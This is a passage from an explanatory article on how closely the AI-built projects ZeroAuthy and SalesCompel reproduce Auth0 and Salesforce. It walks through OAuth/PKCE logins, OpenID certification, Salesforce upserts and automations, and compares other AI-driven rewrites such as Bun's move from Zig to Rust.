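Even a match between the rebuilt code and Auth0's might be weak evidence of copying. When NEC and Intel went to court over NEC's imitation of an Intel processor, NEC hired an outside engineer to write the same kind of code from specifications alone. Some of his routines still resembled Intel's, because there were few ways to write them for a compatible chip. A short passage that matches Auth0's code could have the same innocent explanation. An identical mistake, or a comment with the same odd wording, would be much harder to explain.

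## How much of Auth0 does ZeroAuthy reproduce?

ZeroAuthy reproduces most of what a small website needs from Auth0, but it lacks several features that large companies require. Its first release candidate handles passwords, Google and Microsoft logins and one-time codes, and the project reports that many of Auth0's SDKs work with it unchanged. It has no passkeys yet, and it can't connect to the systems where large companies keep employee accounts.

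### One login in detail

Suppose the bicycle shop has a phone app as well as a website, and a customer taps "log in" in the app. The app opens a browser window and sends the login server a request like this, slightly simplified:

```
GET /authorize
  response_type = code
  client_id = bikeshop-app
  redirect_uri = bikeshop:/callback
  scope = openid email
  state = x7Qp2
  code_challenge = E9Melhoa2OwvFrEMTJguCHaoeK1t8URWbuGJSstw-cM
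  code_challenge_method = S256
```

The `client_id` identifies the app. The `redirect_uri` is the address the browser should return to afterwards. The server must refuse any address the shop hasn't registered; otherwise an attacker could have the reply sent to himself. The app uses `scope` to request proof of who logged in, along with her email address. It generated the `state` value at random and will check for the same value in the reply to make sure the reply belongs to this login.

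Once the customer has typed her password, the server sends the browser back to the app's address with the `state` value and the short code, which works only once and expires quickly. The app exchanges that code for tokens in a separate request:

```
POST /oauth/token
  grant_type = authorization_code
  client_id = bikeshop-app
  redirect_uri = bikeshop:/callback
  code = k9Tz4mWq
  code_verifier = dBjftJeZ4CVP-mB92K27uhbUJU1p1r_wW1gFWFOEjXk
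```

The server returns an ID token, which identifies the customer, and usually an access token, which the app sends to the shop's server when it requests her orders. The ID token also records which server issued it, which app it is for and when it expires. The app checks these details and the token's signature.

Exchanging a code for tokens keeps the tokens out of the browser, as the online tutorial Token Protocol Explorer explains. Sending the tokens straight through the browser would save a step, but browser addresses end up in histories and logs, and a token is useful to anyone who finds it. Only the code passes through the browser, and it is much less useful to a thief as long as the server checks who is submitting it.

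### How PKCE stops a stolen code

That check is PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange, pronounced "pixy"), which dates from 2015. It counters what Authlete's *Proof Key for Code Exchange (RFC 7636)* calls the authorization code interception attack. On a phone, for example, a malicious app might register the same return address as the bicycle shop's app, and the phone could then send the code to the malicious app. The `client_id` is not secret, so without PKCE the malicious app could exchange the code and enter the customer's account.

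A website with its own server can prevent this with a password that only it and the login server share. A phone app can't keep such a password secret, because anyone can download the app and take it apart. With PKCE, the app uses a new secret for each login instead.

The standard's lead author, Sakimura, in *RFC 7636*, gives a worked example in Appendix B, and the two long values in the requests above come from it. The app starts by generating 32 random bytes, which is 256 bits. It writes them as text using an alphabet of 64 characters. Each character carries six bits, so the result has 43 characters:

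`dBjftJeZ4CVP-mB92K27uhbUJU1p1r_wW1gFWFOEjXk`

This is the verifier. The app keeps it and computes a second value, the challenge:

challenge = BASE64URL(SHA-256(verifier))

SHA-256 is a hash function. It turns any text into 256 bits that look random, and nobody knows a practical way to work backwards from the result to the text. The app writes those bits in the same 64-character alphabet, so the challenge also has 43 characters:

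`E9Melhoa2OwvFrEMTJguCHaoeK1t8URWbuGJSstw-cM`

The app sends the challenge when the login starts, and the server stores it with the code. When the app later submits the code, it also sends the verifier. The server hashes the verifier and issues tokens only if the result matches the stored challenge. Someone who steals the code doesn't have the verifier, and even if they also saw the challenge, they would have to reverse SHA-256 or guess a 256-bit number to find it.

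The standard also has a "plain" method, in which the challenge is the same as the verifier. This offers no protection against a thief who saw the opening request, and IAMDevBox's *What is PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange)?* recommends the hashed version, S256. A real app must also generate a new verifier each time, because the values from Appendix B are widely published and would offer no protection.

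PKCE doesn't protect the password. If a customer types it into a fake login page, the thief can start a new login with his own verifier, and the server will accept it.

### Pointing the shop at ZeroAuthy

The shop's website uses nextjs-auth0, Auth0's SDK for sites built with the Next.js framework. The SDK reads the login server's address from a settings file, so the change to ZeroAuthy starts with one line:

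```
before:  AUTH0_DOMAIN = bikeshop.auth0.example
after:   AUTH0_DOMAIN = login.bikeshop.example
```

The SDK sends the same requests as before, but to the shop's own server. ZeroAuthy signs the tokens with its own key, and the SDK fetches the matching public key from that server.

ZeroAuthy has to copy Auth0's choices as well as follow the open standards. OpenID Connect lets each server choose its own addresses for login and token requests, as long as it publishes a list of them. But some of Auth0's SDKs don't read the list and instead add `/authorize` or `/oauth/token` to the domain, because Auth0 uses those addresses. A server that followed the standard but used other addresses would fail with those SDKs. OccupySaaS's home page accordingly describes ZeroAuthy as a server that "speaks the Auth0 Authentication API".

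The shop would still have work to do outside its code:

- It must register the website with ZeroAuthy. If that produces a new client ID and secret, those two settings change as well.
- If it offers Google login, it must give Google the new server's address, because Google also refuses to send people to addresses it doesn't recognise.
- It must move the customers. Auth0 stores only hashes of their passwords and leaves them out of its ordinary export, so the shop would have to request them or ask everyone to choose a new password.
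- It should keep each customer's identifier. The shop's order database may list her purchases under the ID that Auth0 gave her. If ZeroAuthy gave her a new one, she could log in successfully and find that her orders had vanished.

A programmer testing the change with a new, empty account would notice none of the problems with existing customers.

### What the release candidate supports

The release candidate, version 1.0.0-rc.1, came out on 4 or 5 November, and it was still the newest version that Cornelißen described on 23 November. His account follows the project's own compatibility notes. These are the main features:

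| Area | Supported in 1.0.0-rc.1 |
|---|---|
| Ways to log in | Password, Google, Microsoft, or a message sent by email or SMS instead of a password |
| Second check after the password | One-time password, email, SMS, recovery codes |
| Tokens | Code exchange with PKCE, rotating refresh tokens |
| Management API | Most of the requests for users, roles, organisations and Actions |
| Databases | SQLite, PostgreSQL, MySQL |

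A refresh token lets an app get new tokens without asking the customer to log in again. "Rotating" means the server replaces the refresh token each time the app uses it. If an old one is used again, somebody has probably copied it, and the server can cancel the whole series.

The management API lets a company's own programs manage its user accounts. When the bicycle shop hires a mechanic, its staff system could use the API to create his account and give him the "workshop" role. Organisations are groups of users from the same business customer, such as a cycling club. Actions are small pieces of the company's own code that Auth0 runs at certain moments, for instance to refuse a login from a club that hasn't paid its bill.

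"Most" is vague for an API of this size, because a company that uses ten of its requests may find that all ten work or that an essential one is missing. Actions need particular care. Even if a program can store an Action through the management API and read it back correctly, the company also needs the code to run at the right moment with the same information Auth0 would have given it.

The choice of database affects who can use ZeroAuthy easily. SQLite keeps everything in a single file and needs no separate server, so it suits a programmer's laptop. PostgreSQL and MySQL are better for a busy site, and many companies already run one of them.

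The compatibility notes list these SDKs and tools, among others, as working unchanged:

- **auth0-spa-js, auth0-react and nextjs-auth0**, for websites.
- **node-auth0 and Auth0.NET**, for programs on a company's servers. The .NET library covers both the login and management APIs, according to Auth0's *Open Source* page.
- **The Auth0 CLI and the Deploy CLI**, for administrators. The Deploy CLI copies an Auth0 account's settings into files and loads them into another account.

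The home page, which appears to predate the release candidate, lists only the three website libraries as verified. If the longer list is right, the project went from imitating Auth0's logins to imitating much of its administration within about three weeks.

The Deploy CLI could be the most useful item on the list. A company that has used Auth0 for years may have hundreds of settings, and few people may remember why each one exists. If the tool works with both servers, the company could export those settings from Auth0 and load them into ZeroAuthy, and any errors would show which settings ZeroAuthy doesn't support. None of the SDKs that Cornelißen names is for phone apps, so a company with an iPhone app should test it with ZeroAuthy before relying on the general claim of compatibility.

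All of this rests on the project's own tests.

### What the OpenID certification covers

There is also some evidence for ZeroAuthy from outside the project. The OpenID Foundation, which maintains the OpenID Connect standard, added it to its list of certified login servers on 18 October, four days after the code went public. Cornelißen rightly calls this more than a claim in a README file, but he overstates the Foundation's role when he writes that it runs its test suite against the server.

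This is self-certification, in which the people who made the software review it themselves and declare that it conforms, as the OpenID Foundation's *What is Self-Certification* explains. The Foundation supplies the tests and employs specialists to keep them up to date, according to its *Third-Party Support Certification Policy*.

A developer signs in to the OpenID Foundation's test website, chooses a test plan and enters the server's details. The website sends requests to the server and records its responses. For some tests, the developer uploads a screenshot as evidence. Under the Foundation's *Conformance Testing for OpenID Connect OPs*, a server passes if no test fails or stops midway, even if some tests are skipped or produce warnings.

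Afterwards the developer exports the logs, names the exact version of the software and signs a declaration. According to its *Steps for the Conformance Certification process*, the Foundation approves the request before publishing anything. It normally charges a fee, but since 2021 it has waived this for open-source projects that meet certain conditions. The form has fields for the signer's full name and a contact's telephone number and address, so someone at OccupySaaS has presumably identified themselves to the Foundation.

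ZeroAuthy holds certificates for three profiles, each of which covers one part of the standard:

- **Basic OP** covers the ordinary login with a code, as in the bicycle shop's app. "OP" stands for OpenID Provider, the standard's term for a login server.
- **Config OP** covers the page on which the server publishes its addresses and capabilities so that other programs can find them.
- **Form Post OP** covers another way of returning the code, in which the browser submits it to the website as a form. This keeps the code out of the browser's address bar.

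The Basic profile matters most. Another vendor's results, Aloaha's *OpenID Connect Basic OP* (2026), list all 35 tests from a run in July. Most send a valid request and check that the server answers properly. Eight of them deal with the personal details that an app may ask for, such as an email address or a telephone number. A few send something the server must refuse, such as an unregistered return address (one test) or a code that has already been used (two tests). A server that passes has avoided some serious and common mistakes.

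The tests check PKCE less thoroughly than one might expect. The only one named after it, `oidcc-ensure-request-with-valid-pkce-succeeds`, checks that a login with a correct verifier works. No test on the list appears to send a wrong one. A server that ignored the verifier could therefore probably pass, and the SDK tests would miss the fault too. Nothing suggests that ZeroAuthy has this fault. Anyone who installs it can check in a few minutes by changing one character of the verifier and seeing whether the server refuses to issue tokens.

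Much of what a login service does falls outside the three profiles. Aloaha's list has no tests for one-time codes, password resets, Google login, a management API or whether the server blocks someone who guesses passwords thousands of times. The tests for logging out belong to other profiles. In *We are now OpenID Certified™*, Authelia, another open-source login server, named four logout profiles among those it still hoped to pass. Le Monde Informatique warns that ZeroAuthy's certification doesn't validate its security as a whole.

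The certificate shows that ZeroAuthy follows a standard, but not how closely it matches Auth0. The OpenID Foundation's *Certified OpenID Providers & Profiles* lists well over a hundred products that follow the same standard, including Auth0, Okta and an old release of Salesforce. The SDK tests are better evidence of whether an Auth0 customer can switch without rewriting code.

The certificate also covers only the version that the developers tested, though it never expires. ZeroAuthy's entry is more than two weeks older than the release candidate, and the code was changing very quickly in between. The developers can easily rerun the tests and may well have done so, but the October listing doesn't cover code they wrote in November. The Foundation treats a server at a different address as a separate deployment, so a shop that installs ZeroAuthy doesn't inherit the certificate.

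The Foundation writes that a self-certification is only as trustworthy as whoever makes it. It defends the system on the grounds that a company risks its reputation and may be liable if its declaration is false, but the anonymous collective behind ZeroAuthy has much less to lose. However, the test logs are hard to fake because the Foundation's software generates them. The Foundation also publishes the logs behind every successful certification, so a cautious customer can read ZeroAuthy's and see which tests ended in a warning.

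Passing the Basic profile tests within days of publication is still impressive for what is mostly one person with AI agents. The task also suited the agents well. The standard is public and precise, agents can learn from other servers' code, and the test website shows exactly which rule a server has broken, so an agent can correct the code and try again. Agents don't have these aids when reproducing Auth0's undocumented behavior.

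### The missing features

The project lists what version 1.0 lacks and says it plans to add all of it. Most of the gaps affect companies that sell to other companies.

ZeroAuthy doesn't support **SAML**, an older single sign-on standard that many large employers still rely on. Suppose the bicycle shop starts a booking service for corporate bike fleets, and a bank whose sign-in system offers only SAML wants to use it. The shop could connect the bank by changing some settings in Auth0, but with ZeroAuthy it would have to build the connection itself or turn the bank away. ZeroAuthy's Microsoft login might be enough for some business customers. ZeroAuthy also lacks WS-Federation, another older single sign-on standard.

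**SCIM** lets the bank's staff system create an account in the booking service when somebody joins the bank and close it when they leave. Without it, someone at the bank has to remember to tell the shop, and a dismissed employee may be able to book bicycles for months. Business customers expect this feature enough that Better Auth, an open-source login library, extended its support for it in August, as Valverde (2026) reports in *Better Auth 1.7*. A supplier can manage without SCIM if it has a few small customers, but not if it has dozens of large ones.

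**Company directories** are the databases in which employers keep their staff's names, passwords and groups. Microsoft's Active Directory is the best known, and LDAP is the usual protocol for querying one. ZeroAuthy can't check passwords against a directory, which stops a different group of customers from switching. A hospital or factory that uses Auth0 to let staff into its own programs, for example, would have to maintain a second set of accounts alongside those already in its directory.

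**Passkeys**, which use the WebAuthn web standard, replace or supplement the password with a key stored on the customer's phone, laptop or security key. Their main advantage is protection against fake login pages. An attacker can trick a customer into typing a one-time code into a fake page, then pass it to the real site within seconds. A passkey belongs to one web address, and the browser refuses to use it anywhere else, so it can't be used on a fake page. Passbolt's *Mad World* (2026), the release notes for a password manager, adds that many organisations now require this kind of protection before they buy. All the second checks that ZeroAuthy supports involve a code that a customer could type into a fake page.

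The lack of passkeys also affects websites that already offer them through Auth0. A customer who logs in only with a passkey has no password, so the website would have to contact her and set up another login method before switching to ZeroAuthy. That method would be less secure.

**Apple, GitHub and Facebook logins** matter mostly to services for the general public and for programmers. Someone who signed up to a shop with Facebook years ago may not have a password there, and may not remember which email address Facebook passed on. If the Facebook button disappears, she is likely to open a second account or give up. GitHub login matters for programming tools because nearly all their users have a GitHub account. The lack of Apple login is awkward for iPhone apps because Apple requires many apps that offer Google login to also offer an alternative that collects less data, and Apple's own login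 is the usual choice.

These three should be among the easier gaps to close, because ZeroAuthy already has the same arrangement with Google and Microsoft. SAML is harder, partly because other companies' systems implement it slightly differently, and a public specification won't cover all of those differences.

ZeroAuthy also lacks a few less common features. Back-channel logout lets the login server notify other programs directly that a user's session has ended. Without it, an employee who logs out of one program may stay logged in to another. CIBA lets a person approve a request on a separate device, for instance when a call-centre worker needs to confirm a caller's identity. Token exchange lets a program swap a user's token for one with different permissions, so it can call another service on the user's behalf.

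Counting features would make ZeroAuthy look closer to Auth0 than it is for some customers. A club website with a password form and a Google sign-in button might not miss anything on this list, but a start-up that chose Auth0 to satisfy its first corporate buyer would lose the feature it was paying for.

### What it is good for now

The project calls the release candidate an "early preview" and advises against running it in production, where mistakes could expose real accounts. It is much better suited to testing. Many companies run automated tests whenever a programmer changes the code, and some of those tests need to log in. With Auth0, that usually means keeping a separate test account in Auth0's cloud. The tests then need an internet connection and must stay within Auth0's request limits. Programmers testing at the same time can also interfere with each other, for instance if one deletes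 a user that the other's test is about to log in as.

Cornelißen suggests using ZeroAuthy as a stand-in for Auth0 in tests. Each test run could start its own server with an empty SQLite file, create a customer, log her in, check that she sees her orders and then delete everything. ZeroAuthy runs as a container, a package that holds a program and everything it needs, so the testing system can start and discard it automatically. The server has never faced a real attack, but that doesn't matter here because it holds only invented customers and exists for a few minutes.

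The gaps also matter less, because the shop needs ZeroAuthy to reproduce only the features it uses. But where ZeroAuthy and Auth0 behave differently, a test can pass with ZeroAuthy while the website fails with Auth0. The shop should therefore keep a few tests that log in through Auth0 itself and run them before each release.

A company can also use ZeroAuthy to find out how much it depends on Auth0. It can point a copy of its website at a ZeroAuthy server, try everything its customers do, and list what breaks. The project asks people to do this and report the results. For the bicycle shop, the list might contain only an Apple button and a forgotten Action. A company with forty corporate customers on SAML would learn within a day that it can't leave yet, and could work out what leaving would cost.

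## How much of Salesforce does SalesCompel reproduce?

SalesCompel covers a much smaller share of Salesforce than ZeroAuthy does of Auth0. It stores records of companies and the people who work for them, and it answers some of the requests that other programs send to Salesforce. It can't run the code, automations or screens that customers have built inside Salesforce. BornCity reports that the developers describe it as very early-stage. Cornelißen judged on 23 November that it wasn't enough for everyday use.

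### What exists so far

SalesCompel's core is a server program written in Go that stores its data in PostgreSQL. One server can hold the records of several companies and keeps each company's data separate, so a hosting firm could run a single copy for fifty small shops. A fault in that separation would be serious, because one shop might then read another's customer list.

Staff work with the records in a browser, through an editor built with Vue, a framework for web pages. OccupySaaS's home page lists these other features:

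- **Accounts and contacts.** People and programs can create, read, change and delete both.
- **Object descriptions.** A program can ask which fields an account has. An import tool needs this to match the columns of a spreadsheet to the right fields.
- **Limited queries.** A program can ask for certain records, such as every account in Leeds.
- **Upserts.** One request updates a record or creates it if it doesn't exist.
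- **A test laboratory.** It compares SalesCompel's behaviour with Salesforce's public API description.

"Limited" could matter a great deal. Salesforce has its own query language, SOQL, in which the Leeds request looks like this:

```
SELECT Name FROM Account WHERE BillingCity = 'Leeds'
```

The same language can also fetch each account with its contacts or count the accounts in each city. A reporting program that relies on such queries might fail even if the simple one works.

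The most obvious gap for a salesperson is deal tracking. Salesforce calls a possible sale an opportunity, and the record shows how far the sale has progressed and how much it might bring in. The home page doesn't mention opportunities. Someone at the bicycle shop could look up whom to call at a cycling club, but would have no proper place to record that the club is considering buying twelve new bikes.

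Salesforce's API is also much larger than this list. The developer guide that contains Salesforce's *Generating an OpenAPI 3.0 Document for sObjects REST API (Beta)* covers many other requests, including those for recently deleted records, page layouts, saved lists and records of customers' consent.

### An upsert in detail

Suppose the bicycle shop's order system gives every business customer a number and sends any changes to the CRM each night. The CRM may or may not already have a record for customer 11999. The order system could check first and then create or update the record, but another program might create the same customer in between. An upsert (from "update" and "insert") avoids this by checking for the record and creating or updating it in a single request. The order system's number serves as the external ID, an identifier from outside the CRM.

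Salesforce's *Insert or Update (Upsert) a Record Using an External ID* gives an example with a customer called California Wheat Corporation. Written out as a plain web request, it looks like this:

```
PATCH /services/data/v68.0/sobjects/Account/customExtIdField__c/11999
Authorization: Bearer token
Content-Type: application/json

{ "Name": "California Wheat Corporation",
  "Type": "New Customer" }
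```

The first line gives the API version, the type of record, the field to search and the number to look for. The ending `__c` marks a field that the customer added to Salesforce. If no account has the number 11999, Salesforce creates one and returns status 201, which means "created", with this answer:

```
{ "id": "00190000001pPvHAAU",
  "errors": [],
  "success": true,
  "created": true }
```

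Later the order system receives the customer's city and sends `{ "BillingCity": "San Francisco" }` to the same address. This time Salesforce finds the account, adds the city and returns status 200 with `"created": false`. It must leave the name and type unchanged, even though the second request doesn't repeat them.

If two accounts share the number 11999, Salesforce changes neither and returns status 300 with a list of the matches. A compatible server has to do the same, because updating the first match could put one customer's address in another's record. If a program adds `updateOnly=true` to the URL, the server must not create a new record.

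In version 45.0 and earlier of Salesforce's API, a successful update returns status 204 and no text. Programs written for those versions may treat any other response as a failure, so SalesCompel has to check the version number in every request.

Permissions are easier to overlook. Some external ID fields allow duplicates, and a program needs permission to view all data to use them, according to Salesforce's *Upsert Records Using sObject Rows by External ID*, presumably because the list of matches could reveal records the program shouldn't see. A copy without this check could still pass its compatibility tests, just as a login server that accepts wrong passwords could.

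Two programs may also send customer 11999 at the same moment. If both find no match, both will try to create the account, and the database must reject the second attempt if the field is supposed to be unique. But two companies on the same SalesCompel server may each have a customer 11999, so the field must be unique only within each company.

If the external ID is an email address ending in ".inc", Salesforce returns "404 not found", because the ending can look like a file type. This oddity isn't worth copying. Salesforce suggests several workarounds. One is to store the address with an underscore in place of the dot, which should work just as well on a server without the problem. Another is to handle the request with custom code inside Salesforce, but SalesCompel can't run that code.

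### What else happens when Salesforce saves a record

A server could return all the right answers and still leave out most of what Salesforce does with a request. Salesforce's *Triggers and Order of Execution* lists 20 steps that run when someone saves a record. Only a few load, check and store the record. Most of the others run something the customer has set up, such as a rule that blocks duplicates or one that assigns a new account to a salesperson, and emails go out at the end.

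Suppose the shop has set up Salesforce to email the manager about every new business customer. After a move to SalesCompel, the order system sends the same upsert and receives the same `"success": true`, but the manager gets no email. Neither program reports an error, so it might take weeks for anyone to notice, whereas users would complain about a broken login on the first morning.

Running these automations faithfully would mean copying some of Salesforce's peculiar details. Suppose a user changes a number from 1 to 10, and an automatic rule then raises it to 11. Salesforce then runs the customer's code again. If that code reads the old value, it gets 1, even though the number was 10 just before the rule raised it. Some customers' code may depend on this behavior.

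### Apex, Flow, custom screens and extensions

Apex is Salesforce's programming language. It looks like Java, and customers use it to add their own rules, such as refusing an order from a club that owes more than £5,000. According to Salesforce's *What is Apex?*, all Apex code runs on Salesforce's own platform. A company can copy its code out of Salesforce, but to run it, SalesCompel would have to support the whole language, along with its built-in queries and the limits that stop one customer's faulty code from slowing down everyone else's.

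Flow is Salesforce's tool for automating work without writing code. An administrator draws a flowchart, and Salesforce carries out the steps. Salesforce's training course *Go with the Flow* has several examples, such as creating a renewal opportunity when a sale closes. In its main example, a salesperson enters a contact's name in a form, and the flow updates the matching contact or creates a new one, then posts a confirmation for colleagues. SalesCompel could store the contact, but it can't run the flow.

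Customers also design their own interfaces. Some are simple forms made with Flow, and others are screens that programmers write in code. Le Monde Informatique reports that SalesCompel's first version leaves out Apex, Flow and custom interfaces.

OccupySaaS can't, on its own, supply the extensions from other companies that Salesforce sells through its marketplace, AgentExchange. Tarre (2026), *Agiloft adds no-code contract management to Salesforce*, describes one that lets staff start and track contracts from an account or opportunity. The extension syncs with Agiloft's own contract system, so a company leaving Salesforce could probably keep its contracts but would lose their connection to its customer records. Agiloft could build a version for SalesCompel, but has little reason to while hardly anyone uses SalesCompel.

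Customers who use these tools are writing software. Slow-News' *Salesforce is just a really weird web framework* (2025) describes Salesforce as a way to build web applications without fully admitting it. It adds that a department often needs approval for only one purchase, whereas an ordinary application would involve the IT department. SalesCompel would remove that convenience because somebody has to run the server.

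### Moving a company with 20 automations

Imagine a bicycle wholesaler that has used Salesforce for eight years. It has 14 flows and six pieces of Apex code, which makes 20 automations, and several other programs exchange data with its Salesforce account. If it moved to SalesCompel as the project describes it now, this is roughly what would happen:

| What the wholesaler has | After the move |
|---|---|
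| Accounts and contacts | Carry over once someone exports and loads them, though fields the company added need checking |
| Order system that sends upserts | Should carry over with a new address and access token |
| Mailing program that reads contacts | Carries over if SalesCompel supports its queries |
| Opportunities | Need a new feature in SalesCompel, or another program |
| 20 automations | The company must rebuild every one it still needs |
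| Two custom screens | The company must rebuild them |
| Contract extension | The company must replace it or do without |

The order system finds customers by its own customer numbers, so it doesn't need Salesforce's IDs to look them up. A program that has stored those IDs, such as `00190000001pPvHAAU`, will fail if SalesCompel gives the same accounts new ones.

How hard an automation is to rebuild depends largely on when it runs. Suppose three of the wholesaler's 20 automations run on a schedule, including one that checks each night for shops that haven't ordered in 90 days. A programmer could replace these three with short scripts that query SalesCompel.

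Another twelve act after someone saves a record, for instance by telling the warehouse that a shop has changed its delivery address. A separate program could do this by checking for changes every minute. Salesforce has a request that returns recently updated records, but SalesCompel's home page doesn't list it, so the programmer might have to find another way to detect changes.

The last five act before Salesforce stores the record. One refuses a new account if its tax number matches an existing customer's. A separate program would act too late, after the duplicate had been stored. The wholesaler would instead have to change SalesCompel's own code, which the licence allows, and make sure its changes still worked after every update. Any automation that deals with opportunities would have to wait until somebody added opportunities to SalesCompel.

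AI agents could do much of this work, including translating the Apex code. Salesforce also runs customers' Apex tests before it upgrades the platform, so the wholesaler may have tests that show what its code should do. Those tests can't run outside Salesforce either, but an agent could translate them too. It would be harder to find out which automations still matter. If one flow exempts a single shop from the credit check, only someone who remembers the reason can tell whether to keep it.

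Since the wholesaler has to rebuild its automations anyway, it might prefer a CRM of its own that doesn't imitate Salesforce. Curative, a health insurer in Texas, built one in two months and cancelled its Salesforce contract, according to Activant Capital's *So You Vibecoded Salesforce. Now What?* (2026). *Salesforce SMB Customers Switch to Vibe-Coded CRMs* (Semjonova, 2026) reports that smaller firms are doing the same with AI-written code. A company that does this must maintain the software. The trade site Salesforce Ben quotes one executive who called maintenance one of the most challenging parts, though he thought it worthwhile for most businesses of a reasonable size.

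SalesCompel's compatible API would be most useful to a company with many outside programs connected to Salesforce and few automations inside it. It would be less useful to the wholesaler, which has fewer connected programs and more automations.

### Why a login service is easier to copy

SalesCompel's developers have to work from Salesforce's documentation and their own test laboratory, because CRM software has nothing comparable to the open standard, with public tests, that defines much of what Auth0 does. Salesforce alone decides, for example, what its upserts return.

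Most companies want roughly the same thing from a login service, which is to let the right people in and keep everyone else out, but the ways two companies use Salesforce may have little in common beyond lists of names and telephone numbers. A perfect copy of what a new Salesforce customer first sees would still lack the credit checks, screens and exceptions that the wholesaler has added over eight years.

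A copy that could run Apex and Flow would let customers bring much of that with them. Salesforce documents both publicly, so AI agents might be able to build such a copy, but that would be a far bigger project than the current SalesCompel. Auth0 differs only partly, because some of its customers have written Actions that a replacement must run.

Once SalesCompel can record deals, new businesses with no automations would find it easiest to switch to. But these businesses have few programs that use Salesforce's API, so compatibility with it would help them little, and they can already choose from established free CRMs such as SuiteCRM.

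## What have other AI rebuilds of software achieved?

OccupySaaS worked quickly, but in 2026 other programmers used AI to rebuild much larger programs, sometimes faster. They got their best results when the AI could read the original source code and automatic tests could check whether the copy behaved the same way. OccupySaaS's AI can't read the source code of Auth0 or Salesforce, and the project's tests cover only part of what those products do.

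### Bun: 11 days, with the source code

Bun is a free program that runs JavaScript outside a web browser. Its creator, Jarred Sumner, wrote it in Zig, a language in which the programmer decides when to release memory. Mistakes in releasing memory kept causing Bun to leak it or crash. In May 2026, Sumner had Claude translate all 535,496 lines into Rust, a language whose compiler rejects many such mistakes.

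Sumner (2026) reports in *Rewriting Bun in Rust* that the rewrite took 11 days and cost about $165,000 in AI use at list prices. He estimates that three engineers who knew the code well would have needed a year. He works for Anthropic, which bought Bun in December 2025, and he used a Claude model that Anthropic hadn't yet released.

Willison (2026) called the project an "extremely sophisticated piece of agentic engineering", and much of the skill went into organising the agents. Sumner first spent three hours with Claude on a guide to turning Zig patterns into Rust, then tried the method on three files before starting on all 1,448. Up to about 64 agents worked at once. One agent wrote a piece of code, two others looked for reasons it would fail, and a fourth made the corrections. The reviewing agents saw the changed code but not the first agent's reasons for it.

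The agents finished a full draft in about two days, but none of it worked, according to The Pragmatic Engineer's *What can we learn from Bun’s rapid Rust rewrite with AI?* They spent most of the other nine days clearing about 16,000 compiler errors and then fixing whatever failed Bun's tests.

Those tests already existed and make more than a million separate checks. Bun's developers had written them in TypeScript, so they could run on both the Zig and Rust versions. Two days after the first full run, the number of failing test files had fallen from 972 to 23. Sumner accepted the new code once every test passed on all six types of computer that Bun supports. He also checked that the agents hadn't skipped any tests, as some had earlier got rid of compiler errors by replacing the faulty functions with empty placeholders.

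Even so, the tests missed at least 19 faults, which Bun's developers have since fixed. In one case, a line of code both checked a result and added a file to a list. Rust leaves such checks out of the version that users receive, so that version never added the file, although the developers' test version did.

About 4% of the new code is also in blocks marked "unsafe", where some of Rust's protections don't apply. BestHub's *Claude Rewrites 1 Million Bun Lines in 6 Days* reports that critics objected to the number of these blocks. Sumner expects the number to fall, but Bun will always need some because it relies on libraries in other languages.

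### GitHub's Copilot: 14 weeks, with the source code

GitHub took longer, about 14.5 weeks, to move the software that runs its Copilot coding agents from TypeScript to more than 800,000 lines of Rust. Jovanović (2026), in *GitHub Copilot Runtime Rust Migration*, puts the AI bill at roughly $120,000. GitHub advertised the work as "just one engineer and a team of agents", which Jovanović considers true only in a narrow sense, because colleagues reviewed the code and connected it to other software. The engineer, Toub (2026), writes in *Migrating the GitHub Copilot runtime to Rust, using Copilot* that a rewrite of this size "wasn't affordable before agents".

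Sumner replaced everything at once, but GitHub moved its Copilot runtime to Rust in 128 batches and kept releasing new versions throughout, according to InfoQ's *Github Migrates Copilot Runtime to Rust with AI-Assisted Rewrite* (2026). Automated tests and human reviewers checked the batches, though Jovanović notes that no human read all the new code. In GitHub's own benchmarks, the Rust version ran three to six times faster. An even faster mode was still optional in early October.

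*Lessons from building Copilot Cowork* (Jaloza, 2026) describes how Microsoft moved an AI product from Python to Rust while it was in use. *A line-by-line translation of the OCaml runtime from C to Rust* covers the software that OCaml programs need in order to run. The Rust version passes the original's unmodified test suite.

Companies used to avoid rewriting software from scratch. In 2000 the programmer Joel Spolsky called it the worst strategic mistake a software company could make. Engineer's Codex's *The Codebase Rewrite is Back* (2026) cites his warning and lists Shopify, X and Discord among the companies now doing it. In 2021 the software company Sentry converted 95,000 lines from JavaScript to TypeScript, a closely related language. This took about ten engineers a year and a half, and The Pragmatic Engineer's *We need to talk about migrations with AI* estimates that it cost $2–4 million.

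Microsoft is trying to replace its old C and C++ code by 2030, with a goal of "1 engineer, 1 month, 1 million lines of code". *Migrating Legacy Like a North Star Engineer* calls it dangerously naive to suggest that a few engineers could modernise millions of lines within months. Sumner has since roughly matched Microsoft's figure, but he had a million checks to work with, while a bank or government office with a forty-year-old program may have very few.

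### Video games: only the finished program

Hobbyists who rebuild old video games don't have the source code, but they can decompile the finished game. In the strictest form, matching decompilation, they try to write source code that compiles into the same machine code as the original, byte for byte, as GambiConf's *Can LLMs Really Do Matching Decompilation?* explains. Volunteers have done this for all of Super Mario 64.

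A computer can compare the two results and report pass or fail, so an agent can keep trying for hours without anyone checking its work. TechSpot's *Decompilation on Steroids* calls this an "answer key" and argues that it explains most of AI's recent success with old games.

One team's experience supports that argument, because the team started without an answer key. *500+ Billion Tokens Later* (Heumann, 2026) describes three months of rebuilding a popular shooter, which Tom's Hardware's *Dev used AI agents and more than 500 billion tokens* identifies as Call of Duty: Modern Warfare 2, from 2009. After a month, four agents had rebuilt about 80% of the game. It launched, showed its menu and loaded maps, so the team thought the work was going well.

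The code was readable but wrong. The agents had invented some of the game's logic and left out parts they thought unnecessary. They had also replaced simple memory lookups with a far slower method. One of the four agents was supposed to review the others' work, but it accepted departures from the original whenever a code comment gave a reason. Sumner had seen something similar and told his reviewing agents to reject any workaround that needed a paragraph-long comment to justify it.

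Heumann concluded that his team had never properly defined "correct". The agents needed an automatic check that compared each rebuilt function with the original. By October, 83% of the game's functions matched byte for byte. The check may not be the only reason, since the team also postponed its plans to modernise the game, which gave the agents a simpler goal.

Rebuilding the game used more than 500 billion tokens, the fragments of text by which AI companies measure use (unrelated to login tokens). The Bun translation used about 79 billion, mostly to reread text the agents had already seen. If Heumann counted the same way, the game took more than six times as many. His team used flat-rate subscriptions, so it probably paid far less than list prices.

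Other game projects have gone more slowly or started from years of human work. GambiConf's *Starting a Decompilation Project from Zero* describes how a hobbyist using Claude Code decompiled 51% of a 2001 Game Boy Advance game after a year of study and tool-building. Decompilations of GoldenEye 007 and Super Smash Bros. Melee also reached milestones this autumn, but TechSpot notes that volunteers had worked on many such projects for five or six years, and AI mostly finished the last part.

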